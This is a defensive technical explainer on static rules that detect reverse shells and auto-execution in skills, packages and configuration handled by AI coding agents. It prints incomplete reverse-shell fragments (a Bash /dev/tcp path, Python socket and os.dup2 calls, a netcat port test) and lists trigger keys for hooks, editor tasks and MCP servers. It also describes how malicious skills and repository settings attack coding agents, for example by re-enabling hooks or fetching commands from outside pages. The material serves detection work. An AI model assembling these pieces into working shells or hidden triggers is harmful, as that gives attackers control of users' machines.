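# Rule-based static analysis for detecting reverse shells and auto-execution in code handled by AI agents

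## The code AI agents handle and what a static rule can see

Static analysis examines code without running it. In rule-based static analysis, an analyst writes rules in advance, each with a pattern, conditions and a message, and a program reports a finding wherever code matches a rule. A rule pack is a set of rules that people distribute and run together. AI agents are programs in which a language model acts through tools such as a command line and a file editor. They install, write and run a lot of code that nobody has read, so security teams now apply this decades-old method to them too.

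Such rules can target reverse shells. A reverse shell is a program that connects out to another machine and lets whoever controls that machine type commands into a command interpreter on the machine where the program runs. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) shows a real case, an add-on for coding agents named math-calculator. It was described as an arithmetic tool, but line 32 of its script contained a reverse shell. Command interpreters also have everyday uses. MITRE ATT&CK's *Command and Scripting Interpreter* (2020), an entry in a public catalogue of attackers' techniques, mentions long or repetitive tasks among the common uses of shell scripts. It also lists malware, such as BPFDoor, that can create a reverse shell.

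Hostile code also needs something to start it. Auto-execution means that code runs in response to an event, such as installing a package or opening a folder, without anyone calling it.

Reverse shells and auto-execution can both use a living-off-the-land binary (LOLBin), a legitimate program, already installed or trusted, that an attacker can use for harmful ends. The Center for Internet Security's *Living off the Land* names powershell.exe and certutil.exe among the Windows programs that attackers exploit. Volunteers maintain public lists of LOLBins. GTFOBins covers Unix programs, and LOLBAS covers Microsoft-signed files with "unexpected" functions that would be useful to an attacker. Because the program itself is legitimate, inspecting it reveals nothing wrong, and any sign of an attack is in how a script calls it.

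### What passes through an agent

The newest source of unread code is the agent skill, a package of instructions and optional scripts that an agent loads to do a task. Anthropic added skills to its coding agent, Claude Code, in October 2025 and published the format as an open standard that December. OpenAI's Codex CLI and Google's Gemini CLI also support skills. *Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) reports that agents run a skill's code with their own permissions, and that public marketplaces gather skills from code repositories without a mandatory security review.

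Agents also install ordinary software packages from registries such as npm for JavaScript and PyPI for Python. Liu, Wang and colleagues rate both npm packages and skills as having full power to execute code and minimal vetting. They rate autonomy as "none" for packages and "high" for skills, because the agent decides during a task when to run a skill.

Agents also open repositories, which hold configuration as well as source code, and some configuration can start programs. Anthropic's *Hooks reference* describes one such mechanism in Claude Code. A hook is a shell command or other handler that runs automatically at a set point, such as the start of a session. Developers can commit a project's hooks to the repository in a settings file, so every copy includes them.

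Finally, the agent writes code itself: whole files, and single commands that it passes to the shell.

Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (2025) advises users to audit any skill from a less trusted source before using it, starting with the files in the bundle. The same post explains that Claude can run a skill's script without loading it into its context, the text available to the model. This is efficient, but it means that a script can run when neither the user nor the model has read it.

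### One skill folder, three places to check it

Take an invented skill that turns a spreadsheet into a sales report:

```
sales-report/
├── SKILL.md          metadata and instructions
├── package.json      configuration: packages the script needs
└── scripts/
    └── build.js      code the agent can run
```

The Agent Skills *Specification* requires a skill folder to contain a SKILL.md file; all other files are optional. SKILL.md starts with a header that must give a name and a description, followed by instructions in Markdown, a plain-text format in which authors often include commands. An agent loads the name and description at startup, the rest of SKILL.md once it decides to use the skill, and the other files only when the task requires them.

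An attacker could use any of the three files, most obviously the script. A package.json file can specify a command for npm to run during installation. The header of SKILL.md can include allowed-tools, an optional and still experimental field that lists pre-approved tools the skill may use, and Claude Code also accepts hooks there. A scanner that opened only the scripts folder would miss both the npm command and the header settings.

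The earliest place for a check is the marketplace. ClawHub, which distributes skills for an agent called OpenClaw, scans them with VirusTotal, a service that identifies malware. As OpenClaw described the process when the two began working together, ClawHub packs the skill into a ZIP file, computes a hash (a fingerprint of the contents) and looks it up among the files VirusTotal already has. If there is no earlier analysis, ClawHub uploads the bundle and a language model summarises what the code does. ClawHub approves skills judged "benign", attaches a warning to suspicious ones and blocks downloads of malicious ones. It repeats the scan daily. ClawHub has since added other scanners, and the checks described in OpenClaw's *Security Audits* also cover declared permissions, install instructions and package metadata. A scanner at the marketplace has the whole folder, but not the contents of packages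 that are only named in package.json or of anything the script will download later.

A skill can next be scanned at installation, when the user has a copy on disk. ClawScan, the audit system that ClawHub uses, can also run from the command line on a single local folder with only its static scanner enabled. The scanner in *Scan Before You Install* (2026) extracts the instruction document, the supporting files and the skill's declarations before it analyses them. Scanning at this stage also covers skills that came from a colleague or a cloned repository and were never on a marketplace.

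The last check happens just before a command runs. At its PreToolUse event, Claude Code can pass a checking script the tool's name and the exact command. The script can deny the call. If it returns nothing, the call still goes through the normal permission process. This is the only one of the three checks that covers commands the agent has just written, which no marketplace could have scanned. But the check lacks context. For the sales-report skill, the command would be `node scripts/build.js`, which doesn't show what build.js does. Unless the checking script also opens the file, its rules have only a snippet to match, a fragment of code without its file or project.

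### Reading code and running it

The alternative to static analysis is to run the code in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and record what it does. Liu, Chen and colleagues put suspicious skills into containers stocked with fake passwords and keys, gave each run up to 60 seconds, and logged network traffic, system calls and changes to files. If a fake key left the container, they had evidence that the skill leaked credentials. They argue that reading the code is not enough, because a script that reads environment variables (settings the operating system passes to a program, often including secret keys) may be doing routine configuration or stealing credentials.

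A sandbox records only what happens on the path the program takes during that run, so it can miss malicious code that lies dormant until some condition holds. Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026), who allow five minutes per run in *The Devil Wears Markdown*, state that the absence of an observed malicious action is not enough to call a skill benign. Static analysis can cover the branches that never ran. It also takes little compute and avoids the danger of executing hostile code, which makes it a natural first stage. Liu, Chen and colleagues used pattern matching, with help from a language model on the instructions, to narrow 98,380 skills to 4,287 that they then ran. Because the filtering came first, whatever the patterns missed never reached the sandbox.

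### Text, tree and flow

Static rules differ in how much of a program's structure they use.

A text search checks a file for fixed strings or for matches to regular expressions, which describe sets of strings. YARA, a rule format that malware analysts use, works this way and combines strings, byte sequences and regular expressions through Boolean conditions, such as requiring two patterns and excluding a third. A syntax-tree pattern matches the structure that a parser produces from a program's text, so spacing and comments do not affect the result. Data-flow tracking follows a value from where it enters the program to where the program uses it.

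Suppose build.js reads a secret key from an environment variable and sends it with a request to a sales service. A text search for the names of the two functions involved finds both, but it would also find them in a comment. A syntax-tree pattern matches only real calls. A data-flow rule matches only if the key ends up in the request, so it doesn't flag a script that reads a key for one purpose and fetches a web page for another.

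More exact rules need more complete input. A tree pattern needs code that parses, in a language the tool supports. Data-flow tracking also needs the steps between the two ends of the flow, some of which may be in other files. Text search is crude, but it is still used for snippets because it works on any text, including Markdown and half a command. For example, Anthropic's documentation includes a PreToolUse hook that denies a deletion command if it contains the string `rm -rf`. The hook misses the same deletion when the two flags are written separately, and that command goes on to the normal permission process. A bare search for the string would also block a harmless command that prints a warning about `rm -rf`.

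### Counting hits and misses

Three ratios measure a detector's performance. For example, a rule pack might scan 100 scripts, 20 malicious and 80 benign, and flag 24 of them, 16 malicious and 8 benign.

| Measure | Formula | In the example |
|---|---|---|
| Recall | malicious scripts flagged ÷ all malicious scripts | 16 ÷ 20 = 80% |
| Precision | malicious scripts flagged ÷ all scripts flagged | 16 ÷ 24 = 67% |
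| False-positive rate | benign scripts flagged ÷ all benign scripts | 8 ÷ 80 = 10% |

Precision depends on the mix of scripts as well as on the rules. Suppose a rule pack catches 80% of malicious scripts and wrongly flags 10% of benign ones. In a set of 1,000 scripts of which only 10 are malicious, it flags 8 malicious scripts and 99 benign ones, so its precision is below 8%. The mix in a published test can differ greatly from the mix where the scanner will be used. For example, the test set of Truong-Le and colleagues holds 80 malicious skills and 60 benign ones, so precision measured on it is weak evidence of precision in a marketplace where most skills are harmless.

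A script picked at random from the 100 has a 20% chance of being malicious. That chance rises to 67% if a rule matches and falls to about 5% if none does, since 4 of the 76 unflagged scripts are malicious. The 5% holds only for attacks like those in the sample. If no rule in the pack describes a given form of attack, recall for that form is zero, and the lack of a match is no evidence that the script is free of it.

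### Purpose and effect

A static rule can examine only text, but whether code is malicious depends on what someone intends it to do and what it does when it runs. In the sales-report skill, a data-flow rule can establish that a secret key leaves the machine. Whether that is theft depends on who owns the receiving address and what the user agreed to. *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026), which presents a library of skills for research, reports that a security scan of the library produced 34 critical findings. Of these, 28 came from three rules that match when one package both reads an environment variable and makes a network call. The maintainers' review found that these rules systematically produce false positives on skills that read their own key and call their own service.

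Truong-Le and colleagues therefore treat a match as supporting evidence for further analysis and don't base the verdict on it alone. ClawHub's auditors compare what a skill can do with its stated purpose because, in their view, many useful tools need credentials and local commands. Both approaches use information from outside the matched line, which a rule that checks only a single command lacks.

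A scan that finds nothing is harder to interpret than a match, because it can look like evidence that the code is safe. On May 7, 2026, ClawHub audited a skill named Clawhub Publish Security and reported no suspicious patterns, noting that its scanner does not execute the skill (ClawHub, 2026). The report was accurate, but OpenClaw itself tells users that "a clean scan doesn't mean a skill is safe". Unit 42, the threat research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, confirmed this when it found five malicious skills that ClawHub had not blocked between February and May 2026. Two of them sent the agent to an outside web page for the hostile command, so the skill folder did not contain the command for a rule to match.

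What a defender can conclude from a match, or from the lack of one, therefore depends on which features of an attack must appear in the text and which of those the rules describe.

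## What makes a script a reverse shell

A reverse shell needs three parts: an outbound connection to another machine, a command interpreter, and a link that carries the interpreter's input and output over that connection. Each part is common on its own. Programs connect to other machines to fetch updates, build tools start interpreters, and most shell scripts redirect output. Only all three together let a person on the other machine type a command and read the result.

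Firewalls usually block connections from outside but let servers connect out for software updates and similar jobs. *Hunting reverse shells* (Pellitteri and Susini, 2025), by two people who write detection rules at the cloud security company Sysdig, gives this as the reason attackers have the victim's machine open the connection.

On Unix systems, a program starts with three standard streams, for input, output and error messages, numbered 0, 1 and 2. They normally connect to the terminal of whoever started the program. A typical reverse shell connects input and output to the network instead. Redirecting the error stream is optional, though Pellitteri and Susini note that it gives the attacker error messages and the prompt.

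### The parts in shell, Python and Java

The fragments below are incomplete, and 192.0.2.10 is an address reserved for documentation.

| Language | Connection | Interpreter | Link |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shell | `/dev/tcp/192.0.2.10/443` | `sh` | a redirection, an option of a network tool, or a named pipe |
| Python | `sock.connect(("192.0.2.10", 443))` | `subprocess.call(["/bin/sh", …])` | `os.dup2(…)`, which makes a standard stream lead to the socket |
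| Java | `new Socket("192.0.2.10", 443)` | `new ProcessBuilder("sh")` | a loop that copies bytes in both directions |

Bash, the usual shell on Linux, opens a network connection when a script uses a path like the one in the shell row, which is not a file on disk. According to Bucher and Bernát's *Overview of reverse shell techniques*, other shells, such as dash and fish, lack this feature, so a script written for them needs a separate network tool. The most common one is netcat, which sends and receives raw data over a connection. Some versions of netcat have a single-letter option that starts a program with its streams attached to the connection. Other versions leave out the option for security reasons. A script can then use a named pipe (a channel that two programs open like a file) to do the same job, which a rule that checks only for the option would miss.

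Java differs more because it has no call that attaches a process directly to a socket, the program's end of a network connection. Bucher and Bernát point out that ProcessBuilder's redirection methods accept only files. The program therefore has to check the process and the socket repeatedly and forward whatever has arrived from either one to the other. A rule modelled on Python's `os.dup2` would miss a Java reverse shell.

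Some variants have all three parts in unfamiliar forms. Bucher and Bernát tested one built on curl, a common download tool. It asks a web server for a command, runs it, sends the output back in another request and repeats. It keeps no lasting connection and redirects no stream to a socket. Pellitteri and Susini describe a program that never starts a shell. It reads a command from the network and launches the requested program itself, acting as the interpreter. The definition therefore has to be based on function. The interpreter is whatever runs the command text that arrives, and the link is whatever returns the result. Patterns can only list specific forms, and there are many. Bucher and Bernát tested more than thirty methods on Linux alone, some of them through a debugger or a text editor.

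### Neighbours that share some of the parts

Several ordinary or merely risky programs resemble a reverse shell.

| Program | Connects out | Interpreter on this machine | Two-way link |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bind shell | no, it waits for a caller | yes | yes |
| SSH client | yes | no, it is on the far machine | no |
| Port test with netcat | yes | no | no |
| Script that downloads and runs another | yes | yes | no, text only comes in |
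| Remote administration agent | often | yes | yes |

A bind shell opens a port on the victim's machine and gives a shell to whoever connects. Detection rules often treat it as a reverse shell. Elastic's *Potential Reverse Shell* (2023), a rule that watches running programs, matches both connections that a shell attempts and connections that it receives. The difference hardly matters when deciding whether to block a script, since either kind lets an attacker run commands on the machine. It does matter for other defences, such as a firewall that blocks unsolicited incoming traffic, which can stop a bind shell but not a reverse shell.

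An SSH session gives a shell to the side that connects, whereas a reverse shell gives one to the side that receives the connection. Tunnels are harder to classify. A program such as frp connects out to a server and then exposes a local service, perhaps SSH or remote desktop, to people on the far side. The script that installs it contains a connection but no interpreter, because the interpreter belongs to a service that was already there. Ansible Security Scanner, which checks the text files that Ansible uses to configure servers, lists frp and similar tunnels under *Supply Chain Integrity* and covers SSH tunnelling under *Operational Security*. Both lists are separate from its reverse-shell rules, so a defender who loads only the reverse-shell rules gets no warning about tunnels.

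A port test checks whether something answers at an address and then stops. Netcat can do this with one command, such as `nc -z 192.0.2.10 443`, and Bash can do it using only its special `/dev/tcp` path.

Scripts that download and run other scripts are closer to reverse shells. They usually pipe curl's output into a shell. Semgrep, a scanner that can match patterns against syntax trees, has a rule for this form, which warns that whoever controls the server can inject commands. But the server sends only one batch of text and receives no output in return. If the script repeated the download and sent back the output, it would become the curl variant that Bucher and Bernát tested. The downloaded text can also be a reverse shell itself, which isn't visible in the first script.

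Remote administration is the legitimate use that can have all three parts of a reverse shell. With a product such as ScreenConnect, software on the managed computer connects to a server, and a technician can then run commands through it. Pellitteri and Susini report that VS Code remote terminals and the servers behind the code editors Cursor and Windsurf can trigger Sysdig's reverse-shell rules. The machine's owner has agreed to these connections, but the code doesn't show this. A rule can approximate that agreement with a list of approved products or addresses. The Ansible scanner's supply-chain rules, for instance, flag ScreenConnect only in versions with a known security flaw.

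### Nineteen rules sorted by part

Ansible Security Scanner's *Reverse Shell Detection* is a published set of 19 rules that also covers bind shells. Each rule has a one-line description of what it matches, though the description may be looser than the regular expression behind it. The rules fall into five groups based on these descriptions.

| What the description requires | Rules |
|---|---|
| Connection only | Awk, Bash `/dev/tcp`, PowerShell TCP |
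| Connection and interpreter | OpenSSL, PowerShell ConPTY, Python, Ruby |
| A choice of features, so that one part can be enough | Lua, Node.js, Perl, PHP |
| All three parts | Bash interactive, Java, named pipe, netcat, socat, telnet, xterm |
| The name of a tool | dnscat2 |

As described, the Node.js rule is loose because it allows alternative features. It requires a module or object that handles processes or sockets, combined with either a connect call or the path of a shell, so a script that starts a local shell without using the network would satisfy it. Two rules in the group that requires all three parts also have looser alternatives. The named-pipe rule accepts `cat`, which only copies text, in place of netcat. The rule for socat, a relay between data streams, accepts a set of terminal options without the address. The dnscat2 rule doesn't require any of the parts to appear in the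 script, because dnscat2 is a ready-made program that carries a shell over DNS, the system that looks up internet names.

All 19 rules have the severity "critical", so a port test that matches the `/dev/tcp` rule can get the same label as a working reverse shell. A reviewer has to check which rule matched, then look in the code for the parts of a reverse shell that the rule did not require.

### What one part costs and what three parts miss

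A rule that matches a form of connection catches every script that uses it, including harmless ones. Bash's special path, for example, lets simple shell commands send or receive data, according to Splunk's rule for the path, *Linux Shell Pseudo Device Reverse Shell*, so reverse shells are only one of its uses.

Elastic's *Potential Reverse Shell Activity via Terminal* (2020) shows the resulting noise over several years. Elastic sells security monitoring software, and this rule examines the command lines of programs as they start. Version 1 required the name of a shell or zsh's module loader, plus any one of four strings for network access, such as `/dev/tcp/`. By version 112, the rule had a block of exceptions under the comment "noisy FPs", meaning false positives. It now excludes connections to the machine itself, to a host called kafka and to several other named hosts, as well as commands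 that run inside a Docker container under `timeout`, a program that stops a command after a set time. Many of these are probably scripts waiting for a database or message service to start. The rule's guide still calls the activity "unlikely to happen legitimately", which seems inconsistent with the list of exceptions. Each exception also creates a gap, because a command that contains an excluded string raises no alert from this rule, whatever else it does.

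Requiring both a network call and a shell call helps, but a long build script can easily contain unrelated instances of each. The link between them matters more, as another Elastic rule shows. *Reverse Shell Created via Named Pipe* notes that netcat and OpenSSL, a toolkit for encrypted connections, are common tools, but calls it anomalous to capture output in a named pipe that leads to a shell.

The narrowest rules contain most of an actual command. *Suspicious Reverse Shell Command Line* (Roth, 2019) lists such strings. A harmless script is unlikely to contain one by accident, but a string this specific can also miss a working reverse shell that is written slightly differently. For example, one entry for Awk, a text-processing language whose GNU version can open network connections, includes the variable name `s`. It doesn't match the working Awk example that Bucher and Bernát tested, which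 calls the same variable `sock`.

Rules that match program structure can describe the parts of a reverse shell without relying on specific names, but rule writers still have to decide how many of those parts to require. Semgrep's *python-reverse-shell* rule requires a connected socket and a shell call but does not require the redirection, while Semgrep's *java-reverse-shell* rule also requires the copying loop.

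A rule pack can include both kinds of rule if it reports their matches differently. A match on the connection alone is a reason to read the script, while a match on all three parts, where the link joins the matched connection to the matched interpreter, is a reason to block the script until someone has read it.

### What a running process adds

Elastic's terminal rule examines only the text of commands that have started, so it ignores comments and unused branches. It still infers a connection from a string and doesn't check where the shell's input comes from.

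Sysdig's rules instead examine system calls, the requests that programs make to the operating system. Falco, an open-source monitor that Sysdig's team also writes rules for, records these calls. An older rule raised an alert when a call duplicated a network connection as stream 0, 1 or 2. It checked for the connection and the link in the definition, but not for the interpreter.

Pellitteri and Susini describe two faults in that rule. One reverse shell could trigger it several times, once for each stream. The second fault was more serious. A script redirects the streams before it starts the shell, so the rule could not check for a shell at that point and also triggered on harmless programs that connect their own streams to the network.

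To fix this, the team added fields that describe where a process's standard streams lead. The newer rule is checked when a program starts. It matches if the program is one of eight named shells, its input comes from a network connection, and its output or errors go to the same connection. With all three conditions now in one rule, repeated alerts for a single shell largely disappear.

Runtime detection improves on text matching most in detecting the link between the shell and the network connection. In source code, that link can be a redirection, a netcat option or a call to `os.dup2`, and a text rule needs a pattern for each. Once the shell is running, all of these can produce the same observable state, a shell whose input is a network connection. The newer Sysdig rule therefore covers many common reverse shells in Bash, Python and PHP without language-specific patterns.

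The condition still misses some reverse shells. If one process holds the connection and passes data to the shell through a pipe, the shell's input is a pipe and the condition isn't met. If the program launches commands itself, no shell starts. Sysdig has separate rules for these arrangements, some of which follow a sequence of events in which a program starts, connects out, opens pipes, copies itself and finally starts a shell on those pipes. Pellitteri and Susini call the false-positive rates "pretty low" but give no figures, and the remote editors mentioned above are among the exceptions.

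Roth (2021), in *Linux Reverse Shell Indicator*, takes a simpler approach and looks for Bash itself connecting to a remote address, so detection doesn't depend on how the command was written. But testing a port through Bash's `/dev/tcp` path also makes Bash connect to a remote address, so a rule that requires only the interpreter and a connection produces false positives at run time too.

These rules can match only once the code is running. The newer Sysdig rule matches after the shell has started with its streams connected to the network. A static rule relies on less certain evidence but can match before the connection exists.

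### Hard cases

Detection rules often contain the text they look for. Ansible Security Scanner stores examples of vulnerable code in its rule files and has a test file that triggers every rule. Roth's 2021 rule quotes a complete command in its description. Such a file contains all three parts as data, but it isn't a reverse shell by the definition because nothing passes them to an interpreter. A text search will still match it. A syntax-tree rule avoids that match, though it can't rule out that the program later executes the string. Maintainers usually exclude the paths of these files. Ansible Security Scanner's repository excludes its rule files and deliberately bad test files from a different check, GitHub's search for leaked passwords, because they contain strings that look like real secrets. Excluding a folder from reverse-shell rules would leave everything in it unchecked, which is reasonable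 for a security team's own repository but unwise for a skill from a stranger.

Teaching documents differ in how much code they include. Invicti's *reverse shell cheatsheet* (2026) describes typical patterns for defenders and leaves out executable commands, while Bucher and Bernát print working examples with placeholders for the address. Neither is a program on a web page or in a journal, but a code block in an agent skill can act as one, because the agent reads Markdown as instructions and can run the commands in it. If the block appears under "run this before you start", it is part of what the skill does, and the definition applies. A pattern that matches only the block would give the same result if the block appeared under "an attacker might use this".

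OpenSkillIndex's *Hacktricks-skills reverse-shell-defense* page reproduces a skill that is harder for a scanner to classify than for a human reader. The skill is for incident response and authorised penetration testing, in which a tester attacks a system with the owner's permission. It lists `/dev/tcp/`, netcat's program option, `mkfifo` (the command that creates a named pipe) and `os.dup2()` as signs to look for, and includes a command that searches the running processes for similar names, but it never assembles a reverse shell. A rule for any one of those strings would still match it. A rule that required a connection, an interpreter and a way to link them anywhere in the same file would also match, because the document contains all three in separate lists. In a reverse shell, the interpreter's streams have to be attached to the connection, and finding the parts in the same file is a poor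 test of that.

If another penetration-testing skill did contain a working reverse shell, it would fully meet the definition, even if the tester had permission to use it. That permission comes from a contract, and anyone can copy the skill's warning that it is for authorised use only. A reviewer can still compare the code with the skill's stated purpose, as ClawHub's auditors do. A reverse shell fits a penetration-testing skill, but the one in math-calculator did not fit an arithmetic tool.

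Finally, a reverse shell may be split between two files. One Python module opens a connection, and another imports it and attaches a shell. Together they form a reverse shell because the definition applies to the whole program. A rule that checks one file at a time finds a connection in the first and an interpreter in the second, and neither is unusual. To detect the reverse shell, a tool must scan the whole folder and follow the connection from one file to the other. A tool that tracks one kind of data across files may not track another. According to its *Limitations* page, Ansible Security Scanner tracks Ansible's own variables across the files it scans, which is not the same as tracking a socket between Python modules. It can't track data that comes from outside those files or inspect files that a playbook fetches while running.

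## Code arranged to run without being called

A reverse shell in a file does nothing until an agent chooses to run it or an auto-execution mechanism starts it. This mechanism has a trigger, which ties code to an event, and a payload, which is the code that runs when the event occurs. The payload can be harmless, such as a command that starts a local web server when a developer opens a project.

In ordinary execution, a person, an agent or another program specifies the code to run, as with `npm run build` and the build script. The command `npm install` requests only packages, so a script that a package has tied to installation is auto-execution. Skills can involve either kind. If SKILL.md tells the agent to run `setup.sh` and the agent does so, this is ordinary execution because the agent called the script, even though the user never asked for it. If the header of SKILL.md contains a hook,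 this is auto-execution because Claude Code runs the hook's command when the specified event occurs, without a decision by the model.

Persistence means that an attacker's code or access survives a restart. It only partly overlaps with auto-execution. An npm installation script runs once and leaves nothing behind unless its payload does. A command in a login file is both auto-execution and persistence, because it runs again at every login. An SSH key added to the list an account accepts is only persistence, because it lets the attacker back in after a restart but runs no code. An attack can also use auto-execution to set up persistence. Sonatype's *Compromised litellm PyPI Package Delivers Multi-Stage Credential Stealer* warns that removing the malicious Python package isn't enough, because the malware sets up its own way to stay on the machine.

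### Triggers by event

| Event | Where a rule looks | Common legitimate use |
|---|---|---|
| Installing an npm package | `package.json`: `preinstall`, `install`, `postinstall` or `prepare` under `scripts` | compiling a component written in C |
| Building a Python package from source | `setup.py`, or `build-backend` in `pyproject.toml` | compiling a component written in C |
| Starting Python | a `.pth` file with a line that begins with `import`, or any `.start` file | measuring test coverage |
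| Importing a Python module | no key; statements outside any function | setting default values |
| Loading serialised data | `pickle.load` in the program that reads the data | loading a saved machine-learning model |
| Opening a folder in an editor | `.vscode/tasks.json`: `runOn` with the value `folderOpen` | starting a development server |
| Starting an agent session | `.claude/settings.json`: `SessionStart` under `hooks`; `.mcp.json`: `mcpServers`; `.codex/config.toml`: `mcp_servers` | giving the agent project notes or extra tools |
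| Committing or checking out code in Git | files in `.git/hooks/`, or the setting `core.hooksPath` | formatting code before a commit |
| Logging in | `~/.profile` | setting the folders to search for programs |
| A set time | a crontab file, or `OnCalendar` in a systemd timer | making backups |

npm's documentation lists the scripts that `npm install` runs, in order, from `preinstall` to `postprepare`. An older version gives an ordinary example, a package that configures itself in `preinstall` and then compiles in `install`. npm also compiles a package's native component if the package has a file named `binding.gyp`, which describes how to compile it, and defines no `install` or `preinstall` script. A rule therefore has to look for that filename as well as for script keys in `package.json`.

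Python packages come as source archives or wheels. Python's package installer, pip, has to build a source archive before installing it, and the build runs `setup.py` or whatever build program is named in `pyproject.toml`. A wheel is already built, so pip copies its files into place without running any of the package's code. But one of those files can be a `.pth` file containing code that runs the next time anyone starts Python.

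A `.pth` file is meant to list extra folders in which Python should look for modules. According to Python's *site* documentation, Python reads these files at every start and executes any line that begins with `import` followed by a space or tab. The Python Developer Tooling Handbook's *What is PEP 829?* explains that lines that only name folders support editable installs, a common way to work on a package without reinstalling it, so a rule should look only for the import lines. Import lines also have legitimate uses. One participant in the public discussion of *PEP 829*, a proposal to change these files, explains that Coverage.py, which records which lines a test suite runs, uses a `.pth` file to start measuring before each new Python process runs its first line.

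*PEP 829* (Warsaw, 2026) proposes moving startup code into separate `.start` files. A `.start` file contains the name of a function in an installed module, and Python calls that function at startup. Python 3.15 deprecates import lines in `.pth` files but still executes them unless a `.start` file with the same base name exists. Python 3.18 will ignore them. Rule packs will need to cover both `.pth` import lines and `.start` files for years.

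Warsaw argues that a function in a module is easier for people and scanners to audit than a line of code passed straight to the interpreter. A contributor to the discussion of *PEP 829* prefers the change because a scanner can look for a type of file more safely than it can recognise every way to write an import line. The change mostly helps a rule detect the trigger. A `.pth` import line can hold both the trigger and the whole payload, while a `.start` file holds only a name, so the rule has to find the function elsewhere. Python's Steering Council accepted the proposal but asked for a clearer statement of its limits, writing in the same discussion that the changes "do not materially alter the broader threat model."

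Code that runs on import needs no declaration. Python runs every statement outside a function when a program first imports the file, so a malicious statement there looks like any other line of source code. Deserialisation, which turns saved data back into objects, can also run code, because data in Python's pickle format can make the program call functions as it loads. A rule can find the call to `pickle.load` in the source, but the harmful instruction is in a binary data file, which the program may download later.

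When someone scans a skill or repository, the Git hook, login file entry or scheduled job that would run the code usually isn't there yet. Git doesn't copy hooks when someone clones a repository, and login files and crontabs are stored elsewhere on the user's machine. A scanner can still find the command that would create the trigger, such as a line in a setup script that sets `core.hooksPath` or adds a line to `~/.profile`.

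### Agent settings

Coding agents have added several triggers of their own. Claude Code reads a project's hooks from `.claude/settings.json`. Anthropic's reference describes three levels under the `hooks` key: the event, a matcher that can narrow it, and the handlers that run. A handler of type `command` runs a program with the user's permissions. An example in Anthropic's hooks guide uses `SessionStart` to remind Claude of a project's conventions after Claude Code compresses a long conversation.

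A rule has to check `args` as well as `command`. If a hook handler has an `args` list, Claude Code starts the program in `command` and passes it the items in the list, so `command` might be only `node`, with the script's name in `args`. The same applies to hooks in skill headers, which stay active for the rest of the session once the user or the model invokes the skill, unless they set `once: true`.

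The `disableAllHooks` key is also worth a rule because a project can use it to override a user's decision to turn hooks off. A value of false in the project's settings takes precedence over a value of true in the user's own settings, so a user who believes that hooks are off everywhere can open a repository that turns them on again. A value set on the command line overrides the project's.

Agents also start tool servers, programs that give them extra tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP). Claude Code reads a project's server configuration from `.mcp.json`, and OpenAI's Codex reads it from `.codex/config.toml`. An entry for a local server contains the command that starts it. In a malicious entry, that command is the payload, and it runs before the agent uses any of the server's tools.

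Most of these programs ask for permission before using a new folder's settings. Claude Code shows a trust dialog in interactive sessions. According to Anthropic's security documentation, servers in `.mcp.json` have a separate approval prompt, which some sessions skip. Gemini CLI's *Trusted Folders* states that in an untrusted folder the program doesn't connect to tool servers or load the project's `.env` files, which hold environment variables.

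These trust prompts don't replace a scan. When Claude Code runs non-interactively, as it might in an automated build, it registers the hooks of a project's skill even in an untrusted folder. Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever* points out that in Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, approving a folder also approves later changes to it. Defenders who scan a repository only when they first clone it would miss a trigger that arrives with an update, so they have to scan again after each update. Claude Code's ConfigChange event can start a scan when settings or skill files change during a session.

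### Easy to find, hard to judge

Most triggers are easy to detect with a rule. They depend on a documented file and key, which an attacker can't vary as freely as a reverse shell because the program that reads them won't recognise a misspelt version. For example, a scanner that parses `package.json` can list every installation script in it.

A trigger alone is weak evidence of an attack, because legitimate projects use the same keys so that no one has to type a command. Whether the code is malicious depends on the payload, which is often in a different file, such as a script that an npm `postinstall` entry runs.

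VS Code tasks are a good example. A task is a command that the editor can run for a project, and `tasks.json` can tell the editor to run it as soon as someone opens the folder. Suppose a rule applies to `.vscode/tasks.json`, matches any task whose `runOn` value is `folderOpen`, and has the message "This task runs when someone opens the folder." A benign repository for the sales-report skill might contain this file:

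```
{
  "version": "2.0.0",
  "tasks": [
    {
      "label": "preview report",
      "type": "npm",
      "script": "preview",
      "runOptions": { "runOn": "folderOpen" }
    }
  ]
}
```

The rule reports one finding, with the file, line and message. The finding is accurate but doesn't show what the task does, because the task names an npm script instead of containing a command. The command is in `package.json` under `preview`, and that command may run a JavaScript file. A reviewer may have to open three files to learn that the task displays a web page.

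Tasks like this are commonly recommended. master.dev's *Make VS Code Automatically Run Your Project Startup Commands* recommends one for starting a development server and notes that the editor may ask for permission the first time. The VS Code project itself used one to check its code for a class of type errors, according to a contributor's answer to the Stack Overflow question *can i automatically start a task when a folder is opened*. Other editors can read the same file. A bug report on Cursor's forum, *runOn folderOpen tasks are not executed on startup*, says that such tasks run in Cursor when the user opens a folder in an already running window.

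A rule writer could reduce the number of findings by also requiring the task's `command` to contain `curl`, `wget` or `/dev/tcp/`. The table compares the rule with and without this condition on six tasks that run when someone opens the folder. The first four are benign and follow published examples, while the last two are invented and hostile.

| Task | Trigger only | Trigger and command | Where the payload is |
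|---|---|---|---|
| Start a development server through npm | match | no match | `package.json` |
| Check types through npm | match | no match | `package.json` |
| Open two terminals through `dependsOn` | match | no match | two other tasks in the same file |
| Copy files with the build tool gulp | match | no match | gulp's own configuration file |
| Download a script with curl and run it | match | match | on a remote server |
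| Run `node .vscode/setup.js` | match | no match | `setup.js` |

The rule for the trigger alone flags both hostile tasks but also four benign ones, so its recall is 100% and its precision 33%. With the extra condition, precision rises to 100% and recall falls to 50%. These figures come from six hand-picked tasks, so they can't be used to predict performance in practice. However, any attacker can avoid a match on the extra condition by moving the download from the task into a script, as in the hostile task it missed, because the task then contains nothing that the condition matches.

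In the Stack Overflow question *run terminals on vscode start*, the task with the `folderOpen` setting has no command of its own. It lists two other tasks under `dependsOn`, and those contain the commands. A rule that requires the trigger and the command in the same task misses this arrangement. If the rule instead accepts them anywhere in the file, it can combine the trigger from a harmless automatic task with the command from an unrelated task that a developer starts by hand. A task can also have separate commands for Windows, macOS and Linux, so a rule that reads only the main `command` key may check a command that never runs on the victim's machine.

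The file format also makes detection harder. The `tasks.json` file in that question has comments and trailing commas, which VS Code accepts but a strict JSON parser rejects, so a scanner that skips files it can't parse would ignore the whole file. A text search avoids that problem but matches commented-out lines too. The same tasks can be in a `.code-workspace` file, which a rule limited to `tasks.json` would miss.

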